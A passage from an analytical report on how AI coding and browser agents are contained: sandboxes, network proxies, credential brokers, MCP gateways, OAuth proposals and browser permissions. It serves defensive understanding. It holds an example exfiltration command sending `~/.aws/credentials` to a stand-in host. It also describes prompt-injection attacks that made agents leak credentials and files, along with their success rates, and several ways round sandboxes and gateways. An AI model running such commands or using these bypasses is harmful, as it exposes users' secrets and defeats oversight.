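Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine, which has its own kernel, and the code can reach only the folders the user selects. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* explains that Cowork's typical user can't be expected to judge shell commands, so the boundary can't depend on the user to do so. A drawback of this isolation is that companies' security software can't see inside the virtual machine. Docker's version for coding agents uses small virtual machines (Šelajev, 2026), and Docker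 lists Claude Code, Codex and Copilot CLI among the agents that work in it.

### What the products do by default

The table shows the position in late 2026.

| Product | Mechanism | On by default? | Where commands can write | Network access |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Codex on the user's machine | Seatbelt, bubblewrap with seccomp, or its own Windows sandbox | Yes | The project, except protected folders, and temporary folders | Off |
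| Cursor | Seatbelt, Landlock with seccomp, or Linux inside Windows | Yes | The project and temporary folders | Off |
| Zed's own agent | Seatbelt, bubblewrap, or Linux inside Windows | Yes | The project, except `.git` | Off |
| Claude Code | Seatbelt or bubblewrap; nothing on Windows itself | No | The project, except protected files, and a temporary folder | Only hosts that the user or a classifier allows |
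| Copilot CLI | MXC | No | The current folder, `.git`, temporary folders and some caches | Internet on, local network off |
| Claude Cowork | Virtual machine | Yes | Folders the user selects, if the user permits writing | Allowed hosts only |

Users of Claude Code and Copilot CLI therefore have no sandbox unless they or their organization turns one on. Even when turned on, Copilot CLI's sandbox allows internet access until someone restricts it. Wang and colleagues found that another coding agent, Aider, had no sandbox in April 2026. The sandbox in the Zed code editor doesn't cover other companies' agents that run inside the editor.

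Products also differ in what they do when the sandbox can't start. By default, Claude Code runs commands without it. On a Mac, Codex refuses to run a command if Seatbelt can't enforce the chosen policy.

### How the network filter works

To allow some websites and block others, agent programs send traffic through a proxy, which is a program that passes connections on. In Claude Code, this works as follows:

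1. The sandbox removes the command's direct route to the network. The command can only connect to the proxy, which runs outside the sandbox on the same machine.
2. Claude Code sets environment variables that direct common tools, such as `curl` and `npm`, to the proxy.
3. The tool gives the proxy the name of the host it wants, and the proxy compares the name with lists of allowed and denied hosts. The allowed list starts empty.
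4. If neither list contains the host, Claude Code normally asks the user. In auto mode, the classifier reviews the hosts together with the command before it runs.
5. The proxy looks up the host's address. It refuses names that lead only to the user's own machine or to certain other local addresses, and otherwise makes the connection.

The proxy normally doesn't decrypt the traffic, so it checks the host but not the request. It also relies on the host name the program supplies. Anthropic warns that a program might name an allowed host and then use the encrypted connection to reach a different one, a technique called domain fronting.

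Codex turns off network access for commands by default. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, a user who turns it on gets unrestricted access unless they also turn on a separate proxy feature. Someone who only wants to install a package could easily allow more access than they intended.

These filters don't cover everything the agent does online. Claude Code's tool for fetching web pages runs outside the sandbox and follows permission rules instead. Codex's web search uses an index of pages that OpenAI maintains, which reduces the risk from live pages, but a stored page could still contain planted instructions.

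### Four commands under one policy

For example, a developer might use Claude Code on a Linux laptop to work on a project in `~/shop`. The company's own GitLab server, `gitlab.example.com`, holds both the team's code and its registry of JavaScript packages. Git has saved the developer's GitLab login in a file.

The developer turns on the sandbox and sets Claude Code to allow connections to the package registry's host, refuse all other hosts, and never retry a failed command outside the sandbox. Commands can write to the project and to npm's download cache, which npm may need for an installation.

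| Command | What happens |
|---|---|
| `npm install` | It works. npm downloads packages from GitLab and saves them in the project. Any installation scripts run under the same limits. |
| `rm -r ~/photos` | It fails, because the operating system refuses to delete files outside the permitted folders. |
| `curl -T ~/.aws/credentials https://files.example.net` | `curl` can read the credentials, but the proxy refuses the connection, so they stay on the laptop. |
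| `git push --force origin new-checkout` | It works. GitLab replaces the shared branch `new-checkout`, which removes a colleague's last two days of work from it. |

The sandbox can't distinguish the harmful push from the package download, because both make encrypted connections to the same permitted host. The damage happens on GitLab's server, where the laptop's operating system has no control. GitLab could have refused the push if the agent had been using a read-only token.

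A sandbox limits which resources a program can reach, such as files and hosts, while a scope limits which operations it can perform at a service. A read-only GitLab scope would have prevented the push, but it would not have protected the photos or stopped the AWS credentials from leaving the laptop.

Anthropic now thinks of an allowed domain as a "capability grant", because allowing a host makes every function on it available. If the company had kept its packages on a server that did nothing else, the developer could have allowed that server without also allowing pushes.

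A proxy that decrypts traffic could restrict some operations as well as resources. For example, it could recognize a Git push, because a push uses a different web address from a download. Claude Code has an experimental option for decrypting traffic, but the option doesn't add rules about the contents, so a company would need its own proxy to apply them. Someone would also have to write and maintain rules for each service, even though the service already identifies what each request does.

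An ask rule for `git push` is a simpler addition. It prompts the user even when sandboxed commands otherwise run automatically, though it could miss a push inside a script.

### Where local MCP servers run

Local MCP servers often run outside the sandbox that confines shell commands. In Claude Code, they have the user's full access. Codex's permission profiles don't cover them either, so they need separate controls.

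Anthropic first ran Cowork's local servers inside the virtual machine and later moved them out. They were harder to audit there, updates to the virtual machine could break them, and some needed to reach a database or another program on the user's computer. Anthropic now treats them like any other software a user installs.

Copilot CLI runs MCP servers inside its sandbox by default once the user has turned the sandbox on. In VS Code, users choose separately whether to sandbox MCP servers. NTCompatible reports that VS Code 1.112 added this option for macOS and Linux, and that local servers previously had full access to the machine.

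Leaving local servers outside the sandbox can undermine its limits on the shell. If the sandbox stops a shell command from reading a private folder, the model may still read that folder through a local server that offers file tools. In *State of MCP, mid-2026 snapshot*, Chi (2026) calls optional sandboxing MCP's "most embarrassing gap". Chi's company, Archestra, sells software for managing MCP servers, but the criticism is consistent with MCP's own guidance, which recommends sandboxing without requiring it.

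A developer can put everything behind one boundary by running the whole agent program in a container or virtual machine. The boundary then has to allow access to every host that any of the servers needs, so a shell command may be able to reach those hosts too. The boundary also can't limit what a remote MCP server does, because that server runs on someone else's machine.

### Fewer prompts and broken tools

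Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* introduced Claude Code's sandbox in October 2025. The company found that the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%. In February 2026, Cursor reported that its sandboxed agents stopped 40% less often than unsandboxed ones. These figures aren't directly comparable because Anthropic measured prompts and Cursor measured interruptions. OpenAI's *Sandbox* also argues that sandboxing reduces approval fatigue, but gives no figure.

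These companies were measuring their own products, and neither figure shows how often a sandbox prevented harm. Fewer prompts might help users pay attention to the ones that remain. But sandboxed commands can run without a prompt because the sandbox is supposed to contain their effects, and it doesn't contain the effects of a push to GitLab. Unless the developer adds a rule, turning on the sandbox could remove the prompt that would have let the user stop the push.

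Network limits are most useful when the other safeguards have little to detect. In an internal test in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a harmful prompt. The prompt mixed ordinary setup steps with an instruction to send the employee's AWS credentials to an outside address. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 attempts. Because the instruction came from the user, a classifier that looks for the user's consent would probably have found that consent. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the network or on reading the credentials would reliably stop such an attack.

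Sandboxes can also fail. Anthropic says established mechanisms such as seccomp have been dependable and that the weak point was software it had built itself.

More often, the sandbox stops useful tools from working. No vendor seems to have published how many tasks fail for this reason, but Anthropic's documentation describes many cases. Docker doesn't work inside Claude Code's sandbox, and most database tools can't connect because they don't use the proxy. On a Mac, Git can't connect over SSH, and tools such as `gh`, `gcloud` and `terraform` may reject the encrypted connection.

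Anthropic's suggested fix is to run those three tools outside the sandbox, with the user's full access and saved logins. These tools are also among the main ways an agent uses inherited credentials, so on a Mac set up this way, the sandbox doesn't restrict some of the commands that can do the most damage to online accounts.

Claude may also ask to rerun a failed command outside the sandbox. If an allow rule matches the command, Claude Code reruns it there without asking the user. Such rules are common and often broad, so a rule someone wrote months ago to avoid prompts can let a command run outside the sandbox, unless the user has turned these retries off.

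The survey by Wang and colleagues shows how many products let users set boundaries, but not how many users set them. Many users of Claude Code and Copilot probably work without a sandbox, since it is off by default in both.

### Settings that users cannot loosen

Organizations can set sandbox rules for all their employees, usually through the software that manages work computers. In OpenAI's Codex, these rules can be requirements, which users can't override, or managed defaults, which users can change during a session.

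OpenAI (2026) described how it applies these controls when its own staff use Codex. Employees can let Codex read files or write within permitted folders, but they can't turn the sandbox off. Commands can connect to OpenAI's own domains and a Microsoft login page. The policy blocks the text-sharing site pastebin.com and requires approval for unfamiliar domains. OpenAI also lets Codex run a few harmless commands outside the sandbox without approval, such as `gh pr view`, which displays a proposed code change.

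To require the sandbox in Claude Code, an administrator needs three settings that turn the sandbox on, keep Claude Code from starting if the sandbox is unavailable, and prevent it from retrying commands outside the sandbox. With these settings, Claude Code won't start on Windows unless the developer runs it inside a Linux environment.

Even then, developers can loosen some of the rules. If a setting has a single value, the administrator's value overrides the developer's. But Claude Code combines lists from different sources, so a developer can add entries to a list unless the administrator locks it. Anthropic provides locks for the lists of allowed domains and readable folders, but not for the list of commands that run outside the sandbox. A developer could still add `gh` to it.

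Administrators can require GitHub Copilot's sandbox, but a user can still turn it off for the rest of a session unless administrators also forbid bypassing it. The lists of hosts that administrators set on a device can only narrow what a user allows.

Administrators can also restrict which MCP servers employees may use. Codex can check a server's name and identity against an approved list. PromptArmor, a security company, describes a setting that makes Claude Code ignore every list of allowed servers except the administrator's.

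Like other local rules, a managed setting covers only the agent program it configures. A developer could install a different agent, and GitHub would still accept the developer's saved `gh` login from it.

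## Keeping keys out of the agent's reach

If an agent's commands can read a key, they can use it at any host the sandbox allows. Several designs keep the key somewhere the agent can't reach and let another component use it on the agent's behalf. That component can also check the call.

### One request through a credential broker

A credential broker holds a secret and adds it to permitted requests, so the agent never has it. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes one for agents that run in Docker's small virtual machines. Suppose an agent in one of these closes issue 42 on GitHub with a web request:

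1. Beforehand, the developer runs `sbx secret set github --command 'gh auth token'` on the laptop, outside the virtual machine. This tells the broker, a proxy on the laptop, to get the token from the developer's `gh` login when it needs it. The proxy keeps a copy for up to 55 minutes.
2. Inside the virtual machine, the agent finds only a placeholder, such as `proxy-managed`.
3. The agent sends a `PATCH` request, which changes an existing item, to the issue's address on `api.github.com`. The placeholder is where the token should be.
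4. According to Docker, a request that can't go through the proxy doesn't leave the virtual machine. The proxy decrypts the request and checks whether the host is one that may receive the GitHub token.
5. The proxy overwrites the placeholder with the real token and sends the request to GitHub.
6. GitHub checks the token and closes the issue.

If a prompt injection makes the agent send out everything in its environment, the attacker gets a useless placeholder, so this protection doesn't depend on the model behaving well.

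The proxy in this example checks a request's destination but not its operation. A stricter broker could also check the method and the address, allowing `PATCH` for issue 42 and only `GET`, which reads, for everything else. But the method doesn't always distinguish reads from writes. `gh issue close` uses GitHub's GraphQL interface, where reading an issue and closing one are both `POST` requests to the same address, so the broker would have to examine the body too.

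Without such a rule, the token's own scopes set the limit, so the agent could still publish private code as a gist.

The broker runs where the agent can't alter it, which fully restores one of the four properties of a service-side check. The developer can also cut off the agent's access separately, because removing the secret from the broker takes effect in running sandboxes and leaves the developer's own `gh` login working. GitHub still receives the `gh` token, though, so it can't identify the agent or log its actions separately. A fine-grained token that only the broker uses would improve on this.

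### Where brokers fall short

A broker protects the user's key, but the agent might use someone else's. Anthropic describes an attack on Cowork in which a file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and the attacker's own API key. Claude followed the instructions and uploaded other files from the folder to the attacker's Anthropic account. The network filter allowed the upload because `api.anthropic.com` was an allowed host. Anthropic fixed this with a proxy that passes only requests carrying the session's own token. A broker therefore has to reject or replace any key the agent supplies, as well as add the right one.

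A service can also send the secret back, for example in an error message that repeats the request. For some kinds of secret, Docker's proxy searches the reply and masks any match. It can miss a secret that the service splits across several fields, and it doesn't inspect WebSocket messages, which some services use for live connections.

Some credentials don't fit the placeholder design. An AWS request contains a signature computed from the key, not the key itself, so Claude Code's version of the broker has to re-sign the request with the real key. Anthropic lists forms the broker can't re-sign, such as streaming uploads. For SSH, Docker forwards signature requests to the laptop. The agent can't copy the private key, but it can request a signature at any time.

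To set up Claude Code's broker, the user must turn on the sandbox and the experimental option for decrypting traffic, then list each credential to hide. If the user doesn't say which hosts may receive a credential, the proxy will supply it to every allowed host. If the user's pattern for finding a secret in a file matches nothing, commands on Linux can by default read the whole file.

The broker is an attractive target because it holds the keys and can read the traffic. Docker advises users not to keep secret-fetching helper scripts in folders the agent can write to, because the agent could edit a script that the laptop later runs with the developer's full access.

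Hosted agents make this arrangement easier because the provider controls both the sandbox and the proxy outside it. In Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents*, the proxy takes a token tied to the session, gets the matching OAuth token from a vault and calls the MCP server. Anthropic considered relying on narrow tokens inside the sandbox, but decided that this meant guessing what an increasingly capable model couldn't do with one. That is a good reason to keep the token outside the sandbox, but narrow scope still matters because the agent can cause any request the proxy accepts.

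In its review of the product, the vendor Pluto Security calls the vault the strongest security feature but notes that the sandbox has unrestricted internet access by default. A prompt-injected agent couldn't steal the key, but it could send out data it had used the key to fetch.

*Credential Brokering for AI Agents, Explained*, by the secret-storage vendor Infisical, lists similar designs from Vercel, Cloudflare and LangChain. Vendors often describe these designs as "injecting" credentials, which can be confusing. NVIDIA, for example, uses the word for two different things in its OpenShell sandbox. A router outside the sandbox adds the key for the AI model, but other credentials go into the sandbox, where the agent may be able to read them.

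A secret wrapper is a weaker alternative for local MCP servers and restores none of the four properties. The one that Skverer released with his study gets the key from AWS's secret store and starts the server with the key in an environment variable. This keeps the key out of the configuration file and lets a company replace the key regularly without editing that file on every laptop. But the server still holds the key, and Skverer acknowledges that the key can be as broad and long-lived as before. The wrapper also needs its own login to the store, and an agent with a shell might use that login too.

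### Gateways

An MCP gateway is a single endpoint, usually run by a company, that passes tool calls on to many MCP servers. An employee's agent program logs in to the gateway with OAuth, and the gateway lists only the tools that the employee's group may use. When the model calls the tool for closing a GitHub issue, the gateway checks the call, adds the credential for the GitHub server and forwards the call there, so the agent program holds only a token for the gateway.

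All four properties can hold at the gateway, which can identify the agent program, hide tools, refuse particular arguments, keep its own log and cut off one program. GitHub may receive much less information. With a shared account, the service receives the same bot identity for every user, according to the documentation for Envoy AI Gateway, an open-source gateway. This is fine for a weather service but wrong where people have different permissions. If the bot can read every repository and the gateway's rules have a gap, an employee's agent could read code that the employee can't. A gateway can avoid this by forwarding the user's own credential. Maxim AI, a vendor, says its gateway can also exchange the user's login for a short-lived token that works at one server.

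Three large companies have described their gateways publicly. Cloudflare's *Scaling MCP adoption* (2026) says the company decided early on that local servers were a liability because employees chose and updated them individually. A central team now runs remote servers, with write tools off by default. Finance staff, for instance, could get a portal with only the code repository's read-only tools. Cloudflare sells the products it used for this setup.

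Uber's gateway covers more than 10,000 internal services. According to the Agentic AI Foundation's *How Uber Runs 60,000 AI Agent Tasks Per Week With MCP*, a language model drafts the tool descriptions and the team that owns each service decides which tools to expose. The gateway removes personal information from results and blocks write operations on critical services.

Pinterest's gateway is smaller. sysdesign-wiki's *Building an MCP Ecosystem at Pinterest* (2026) quotes the company's report of 66,000 calls a month from 844 users. The company dates these figures to January 2025, only about two months after MCP's release, so the year may be a mistake.

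That is about 78 calls per user per month. Copilot's coding agent averaged about 240 tool calls per user in one week, according to Microsoft's records. The comparison is rough, since most of Copilot's calls only touch local files, but it suggests that even a busy gateway may cover only a small part of what agents do. None of the three companies seems to have published how many harmful calls its gateway stopped.

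### Going around the gateway

The main objection to gateways is that an agent with a shell can bypass them, for example by using the developer's saved `gh` login. Uber's coding agents can also add local servers with a command-line tool.

Cloudflare looks for unapproved servers by scanning employees' traffic for known MCP host names, addresses ending in `/mcp`, and MCP message names such as `tools/call`. This can find remote servers, but a local server exchanges those messages with the agent program inside the laptop, so the network carries only the server's ordinary requests to GitHub or another service. Cloudflare's *MCP governance* defines "Shadow MCP" as employees running unmanaged local servers against sensitive resources, which this scan is least able to detect.

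To close the gap, the sandbox must have no direct network route and no other usable credential for the same service. Docker can provide both, because its MCP gateway runs outside the virtual machine. But if Docker's credential broker also adds the developer's token to GitHub requests, `gh` works inside the sandbox and bypasses the gateway's rules. To prevent this, the developer would have to give the broker a read-only token or none, and the agent could then no longer push code over HTTPS. Docker also warns that local servers behind its gateway run on the laptop with the laptop's permissions, so a careless choice of server can reopen the gap.

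A gateway therefore seems well suited to agents on a company's own platform, where the company controls the network. On an ordinary developer laptop, it mostly governs agents that have no reason to bypass it.

### Approved servers and registries

Companies that operate gateways usually also decide which servers may run. At Pinterest, every server beyond a one-off experiment needs an owning team, an entry in the internal registry, and approval from security and legal reviewers. Pinterest allows local servers for experiments.

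According to the Model Context Protocol project, the public MCP Registry holds only descriptions, which point to packages hosted on npm and similar sites. An entry helps a user find the right package, but it doesn't show that the package is safe.

Approved-server lists reduce the risk of running malicious or abandoned code. They don't restore any of the four properties, because they control which servers may run but don't limit what a call may do.

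Approval can also become outdated. Anthropic points out that users can read a local server's code and keep it at one version, while the operator of a remote server can change it at any time after approval. Even an unchanged connector can bring in a document with planted instructions.

### Moving to a remote server

Despite that drawback, a remote server lets the service require its own grant. A developer who replaces a local GitHub server and its static key with GitHub's remote server gets all four properties, as far as GitHub's scopes allow. Switching to a remote server isn't enough by itself, since many don't use OAuth. A remote server also can't open files on the laptop, and a fault on the operator's side can affect every user at once.

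In a company, each employee normally has to approve each server separately. In June 2026, the Model Context Protocol project declared an extension called Enterprise-Managed Authorization stable, which removes that step:

1. The employee logs in to the agent program through the company's identity provider, the system that handles staff logins.
2. The identity provider checks the administrator's policy and issues a signed statement, called an ID-JAG, for a particular MCP server.
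3. The agent program exchanges the statement for an access token at that server's authorization server, without showing a consent page.
4. The server checks the token on each call as usual.

Okta was the only identity provider at launch. Claude's apps, VS Code and services including Asana, Figma and Linear supported the extension. WorkOS, a vendor of login software, reports that Datadog, Notion and Slack followed. In Anthropic's *Centrally manage authorization for MCP connectors*, a customer says 2,000 employees are connected this way with "zero extra steps", which is evidence of convenience but not of security.

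The service still does its own check. Atlassian, whose support was in private beta when announced, validates the company's statement before issuing its own scoped tokens. The employer now gives permission instead of the user. That seems reasonable for a work account, but one mistaken policy could connect every employee's agent to the wrong service. The identity provider also becomes a point of failure for all those agents.

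An agent program that doesn't support the extension can use a gateway that does. The Agentic AI Foundation describes one, agentgateway, that performs the exchange for such programs. The service would then probably receive the gateway's name as the client instead of the agent program's.

### Tokens for one task

A company can also replace a static key with a token that expires when the task ends. Cowork's virtual machine, for instance, gets a token with reduced permissions for each session, and Anthropic can revoke it without affecting the user's own token. Such tokens make it possible again to revoke the agent's access separately from the user's, and the issuer can give the agent fewer permissions than the user has. The token identifies the agent only if the issuer puts the agent's name in it.

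DataRobot's *Credentials should never reach the model* argues that even short-lived tokens should be kept behind a broker, because a stolen token works until it expires. This is a real risk during an attack, since an agent can do a lot of harm in ten minutes. Short lifetimes help more with keys that people leave in logs and configuration files, where an attacker may find them months later, after they have expired.

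The new weak point is whatever issues the tokens. If the agent can use the developer's saved login to request another token, the expiry time does little to limit the agent's access.

Several proposals would standardize tokens that name an agent and its task. Most are Internet-Drafts, which anyone can submit to the IETF, the body that standardizes OAuth. A draft expires after about six months unless someone renews it, and many never become standards.

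*Transaction Tokens For Agents* (Raut, 2026) proposes a token that identifies both the user and the agent. When one agent hands work to another, a token service replaces the token but keeps the original identities, so the last service in the chain can identify who started the job. This version of the proposal was due to expire on November 23, 2026.

*OAuth Profile for Delegated AI Agent Authorization* (Kumar, 2026) would have OAuth identify each running copy of an agent, which could distinguish two agents on the same laptop. It would also bind each token to its holder, so stealing a token would not be enough to use it. *AI-Auth* (Kasselman, 2026) is broader and combines existing OAuth methods with transaction tokens. *AI Agent Authorization* (Liu, 2026) relates agent authorization to transaction tokens and to ID-JAG. The first draft expires in March 2027 and the other two in January 2027.

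*OAuth Transaction Authorization Challenge* (Rosomakho, 2026) may be the most relevant proposal for prompt injection. It would add a step that ordinary OAuth lacks, letting a service respond to a risky request by requiring approval for that one operation. The client would send the requirement to the authorization server, which could ask the user. A file store could then require a new decision before an agent overwrote a contract, even if the agent's token already permitted writing. Services would still have to choose which operations require approval. The May version was due to expire in early November.

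ID-JAG is further along. The IETF's OAuth working group adopted the draft as its own work in September 2025, according to gentic.news.

SEP-1933, a proposal in the Model Context Protocol (MCP) project, would let a program prove its identity with a short-lived token from the platform it runs on, so it wouldn't have to register as an OAuth client. The proposal, still a draft in late August 2026, relies partly on OpenID Connect, the OpenID Foundation's login standard. The MCP project already lists as final a related proposal that lets a program log in as itself, with no user present. Both suit agents in the cloud better than agents on a laptop, where no platform normally verifies the agent's identity separately from its user's.

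All these proposals depend on the agent program requesting a token. An agent that runs `gh` with a saved login already has one, so services would also have to stop accepting the old credentials, or users would have to keep them away from the agent.

The US standards agency NIST is at an earlier stage. In February, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026) outlined a possible project and asked for comments. It received more than 600 formal responses, according to *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026). In mid-November, NCCoE, the NIST center responsible, offered a summary of the comments on its page *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization* and was still collecting more. It had not yet announced a demonstration.

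## Limits built into browsers

A browser works a little like a credential broker, because the agent can use a login without reading the cookie. Hiding the cookie from the agent therefore adds little protection, and a useful limit has to restrict what the agent does on the page.

Unlike the site, the browser has access to the user's task, so the browser's maker could notice a $90 order for someone who asked for a cheap charger. But the browser often can't determine what a click will do, because a click can open a link or delete an account depending on the site's code.

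### Keeping the agent away from the user's logins

The simplest limit is to start the agent without logins. OpenAI's Atlas browser had a logged-out mode in which the agent ignored existing cookies, according to OpenAI's *Using Ask ChatGPT sidebar and ChatGPT agent on Atlas*. But Atlas stopped working on August 9, 2026, as International Business Times' *OpenAI Upgrades ChatGPT for Chrome So It Can Read Your Tabs* (2026) reports, and OpenAI moved many of its features to a Chrome extension.

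ChatGPT can work in three browsers, and each handles logins differently. The Chrome extension uses the sessions the user already has. The browser inside the ChatGPT desktop app keeps its own state, so the user may have to sign in again. The cloud browser runs on a separate computer and has its own cookies. OpenAI's *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT* explains that the user types passwords into a form that sends them straight to the remote browser, where the model can't see them. Before that, a second model checks the sign-in request for signs of phishing.

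An agent with no logins can't read the user's email or spend money from a saved card, but it also can't do much of what people want from a browser agent. Once the user signs in to a site in the cloud browser, the agent can act there as the user, and the login stays available for later tasks until it expires or the user clears it. A user who signed in to compare electricity plans might leave that account open to an agent booking a restaurant the following week. Separate logins limit which accounts are at risk but not what can happen in each one.

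### Permission for a site

Most browser agents can ask before they use a new site. According to *Codex Chrome extension*, OpenAI's extension asks about each new host, such as `example.com`, and the user can allow the host for the current chat, allow it permanently or refuse. The cloud browser also asks by default, but users can let ChatGPT review addresses itself and stop only when one seems unsafe.

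Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* describes three modes for Claude in Chrome. In Manual mode, Claude asks before each action, and the user can allow one action or everything on that website. In Auto mode, the default in the newer side panel, Claude reviews its own actions and usually continues without asking. The third mode skips approvals. Some sites require approval for every action.

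Makers also restrict some categories of site. Anthropic's *Using Claude in Chrome safely* lists adult sites and known sources of pirated content as blocked, and Claude asks before it opens financial sites. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) explains that Chrome's agent, auto browse, asks before it opens certain banking and medical sites. Chrome compares the address with a fixed list, so a misled model can't bypass the check, but the check covers only the sites on that list.

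A permission to act on a site is much broader than most OAuth grants, though the two can look similar. In the contract drafts example, the user gave the agent the scope `files:read`, so the file store refused when the agent followed planted instructions to overwrite a draft. If the user had instead allowed the agent to use the file store's website, that one permission would have covered reading, overwriting, deleting and sharing the files, as well as the account settings. The closest OAuth equivalent is a token with every scope the service offers, but even that would leave out anything on the website that no scope covers.

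The site doesn't receive the permission either, so it can't enforce or log it. Chrome may not enforce it. To work, OpenAI's extension needs Chrome's permission to read and change all the user's data on all websites. OpenAI's software then restricts that access with prompts, an allowlist and a blocklist. The model can't change that software by producing a different answer, but a bug in it could expose every site where the user is logged in.

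Unlike many OAuth grants, site permissions can end with the task, so a user who allows a site for one chat doesn't have to remember to revoke access later.

### Confirmations and forbidden actions

Because site permissions are broad, browser agents also have rules for particular actions. OpenAI's *Using site tools in the ChatGPT desktop app* says ChatGPT asks before it makes purchases, deletes data, changes account permissions or sends messages, even on a site the user has approved. Before sending sensitive information, ChatGPT explains what it will send, where and why.

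| Product | Purchases and payments | Messages | Passwords |
|---|---|---|---|
| Chrome's auto browse | Tries to pause and ask, or hands over the last step | Tries to pause and ask, or hands over the last step | Asks before using a saved password, which the model can't read |
| ChatGPT's built-in browser | Asks | Asks | The user types them on the website |
| ChatGPT's cloud browser | Asks in the chat | Asks if the message could create a commitment or be hard to reverse | The user types them into a secure form |
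| Claude in Chrome | Forbidden | Depends on the mode | Asks before entering sensitive information |

Google has extended this arrangement to Gemini Spark, an agent that can use the user's Chrome logins with permission. It hands control back to the user before payments, according to Digital Trends' *Gemini Spark can now use your Chrome logins and saved passwords*. OpenAI's *ChatGPT agent* describes a stricter "watch mode" for certain sites, in which the user has to supervise the agent.

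Claude also has to ask before it grants authorizations, in every mode. Without such a rule, an agent can approve an OAuth consent page itself, as Hossen showed.

All of these rules work only if something first recognizes the action. A "Place order" button is easy to recognize, but a button labeled "Continue" may also charge a card. Parker appropriately says only that the agent "will try to pause" before such actions. Anthropic's list of prohibited actions includes carrying out instructions from emails or web content. This amounts to forbidding the model to fall for a prompt injection, and no browser setting can guarantee that it won't.

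WebMCP, a proposed standard, could make actions easier to recognize. A website offers named tools, such as one that updates a shopping cart, and ChatGPT calls them instead of finding the right button. ChatGPT reviews each call and the information it would send. But the calls run in the user's signed-in session, so the site makes no separate decision about the agent. OpenAI also warns that a site's tools may do things the visible page does not offer.

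### Comparing each action with the task

Chrome has the most elaborate published design among these products. Parker describes a check that works roughly as follows:

1. The user gives Gemini a task.
2. Gemini reads the page and proposes the next action. Text on the page could mislead it at this point.
3. A separate Gemini model, the User Alignment Critic, receives information about the proposed action but no unfiltered page content. It decides whether the action serves the user's goal.
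4. If it approves, Chrome carries out the action. If it refuses, Gemini has to plan again, and after repeated refusals the agent can return control to the user.

Planted text can't reach the critic directly. But the critic has less information to judge by, much like the classifier in Claude Code's auto mode, which doesn't see tool results. If the user asked for the charger with the best reviews, the critic could approve a click on the wrong charger because it can't see the reviews.

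Chrome also limits which sites the agent can use. For each task, a design called Agent Origin Sets keeps one list of origins that Gemini may only read and another of origins that it may both read and act on. The model doesn't receive frames from origins on neither list, such as ads. A gating function adds an origin only if it seems relevant to the task. Chrome also restricts model-generated web addresses to known public ones, so that the agent can't leak private data in an address.

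This limits where stolen data can come from and go to. If the task is to put a recipe's ingredients into a grocery cart, the agent doesn't need to open the user's bank site, and a prompt injection on the recipe page couldn't send it there unless the gating function also wrongly allowed it. The limit wouldn't help when the task itself involves both the private data and the attacker's page.

Google launched a simpler version that tracked only the list of origins where the agent may read and act. According to Google's *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse*, the user reviews a plan, and Gemini then chooses the sites and may share personal information with them.

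In November 2026, Google proposed further limits. Qué!'s *Google le pone correa a los agentes IA de Chrome* (2026) describes restricted sessions in which agents need permission to navigate, click or run scripts. Europa Press' *Google propone un sistema de permisos en Chrome para restringir las acciones* (2026) also describes this as a proposal still in progress, so it doesn't yet protect anyone. Permissions for kinds of action would be closer to OAuth scopes than permissions for whole sites are. They would still be quite coarse, since permission to click on a bank's page includes permission to click "Transfer".

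### How often attacks succeed

The first published figures for Claude's extension come from its pilot. eWeek's *Claude-for-Chrome Pilot* reports that safeguards cut the success rate of attacks from 23.6% to 11.2%, and from 35.7% to zero for attacks aimed at browsers, such as malicious text hidden in form fields. These figures are out of date because both the models and the safeguards have changed since then. For example, the pilot blocked financial sites, which Claude may now open with permission.

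More recent tests still found high rates. In a June 2026 study of how agents carry data across the same-origin boundary, Wang and colleagues ran the commercial browsers by hand. The agent first handled private information on one page, such as an insurance claim, and then visited a second page with planted instructions. The team counted a success only if the agent wrote exactly the targeted information into the second page.

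The study gives results for 50 combinations of pages, with three runs each. Added together, they show that attacks succeeded in 99 of 150 runs on Atlas with GPT-5.5. On Perplexity's Comet, attacks succeeded in 92 runs with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 100 with Gemini 3.1 Pro, also out of 150 each. The attacks worked most often on pages imitating Google Forms, where they succeeded in 29 of 30 runs on Atlas. The attacker controlled the whole form, and a form that asks for personal details doesn't look unusual. On pages imitating GitHub, where the attacker controlled only part of the text, attacks succeeded in 12 of 30 runs on Atlas.

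These rates show that two widely available products could fail most of the time against a prepared attacker in mid-2026. They don't mean that an ordinary web page has a 60% chance of stealing data, because the team wrote each attack for a particular page. They also can't be compared directly with the 11.2% from Anthropic's pilot, which used different attacks.

Detecting the planted text is difficult too. Wang and colleagues tested five detectors. Perplexity's BrowseSafe missed 41% to 64% of the contaminated pages, depending on the type of site. Another, WebSentinel, missed at most 1% but raised false alarms on 6% to 44% of clean pages. A browser that often stopped on clean pages would annoy its users, so makers are likely to prefer a detector that misses more contaminated pages.

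### A same-origin policy for agents

Wang and colleagues also built a defense called SOPGuard, which tries to restore the same-origin policy for data that an agent carries. They added it to BrowserOS, an open-source browser with a built-in agent. Suppose an agent has read a prescription on a pharmacy's website and then fills in a form on another site:

1. When the agent reads the pharmacy page, SOPGuard stores the text in a database and labels it with the page's origin.
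2. If the agent writes a summary of the prescription, SOPGuard asks the model which stored items it used. The summary inherits the labels of all of them.
3. Before the agent types text into the form, SOPGuard compares the text's labels with the form's origin.
4. If any label differs, a pop-up names the two origins and asks the user to approve or deny the action.

A text *x* that comes from stored items *J* carries all of their origin labels, so *O(x)* = ∪ *O(j)* for all *j* in *J*. SOPGuard raises a warning if *O(x)* contains any origin other than that of the page the agent is trying to write to.

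The second step is the weakest because it relies on the same model that an attacker is trying to mislead. SOPGuard could avoid this by giving every new text the labels of everything the agent has read, but then almost any typing late in a session would produce a warning. In tests with data from 2 to 10 origins, GPT-5.4's labels overlapped with the correct ones by at least 95.5%. Attacks that told the model to treat the current page as the only source raised the violation rate only slightly, though stronger attacks may be possible.

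SOPGuard reduced violations on the main benchmark to zero. Without it, BrowserOS with GPT-5.4 leaked data in 3% to 100% of runs, depending on the pages. SOPGuard also prevented leaks that involved no attacker. When a page embedded another site in a frame, BrowserOS without SOPGuard copied the framed data into its summary every time. It did not leak data when it visited the two pages one after the other with no planted text.

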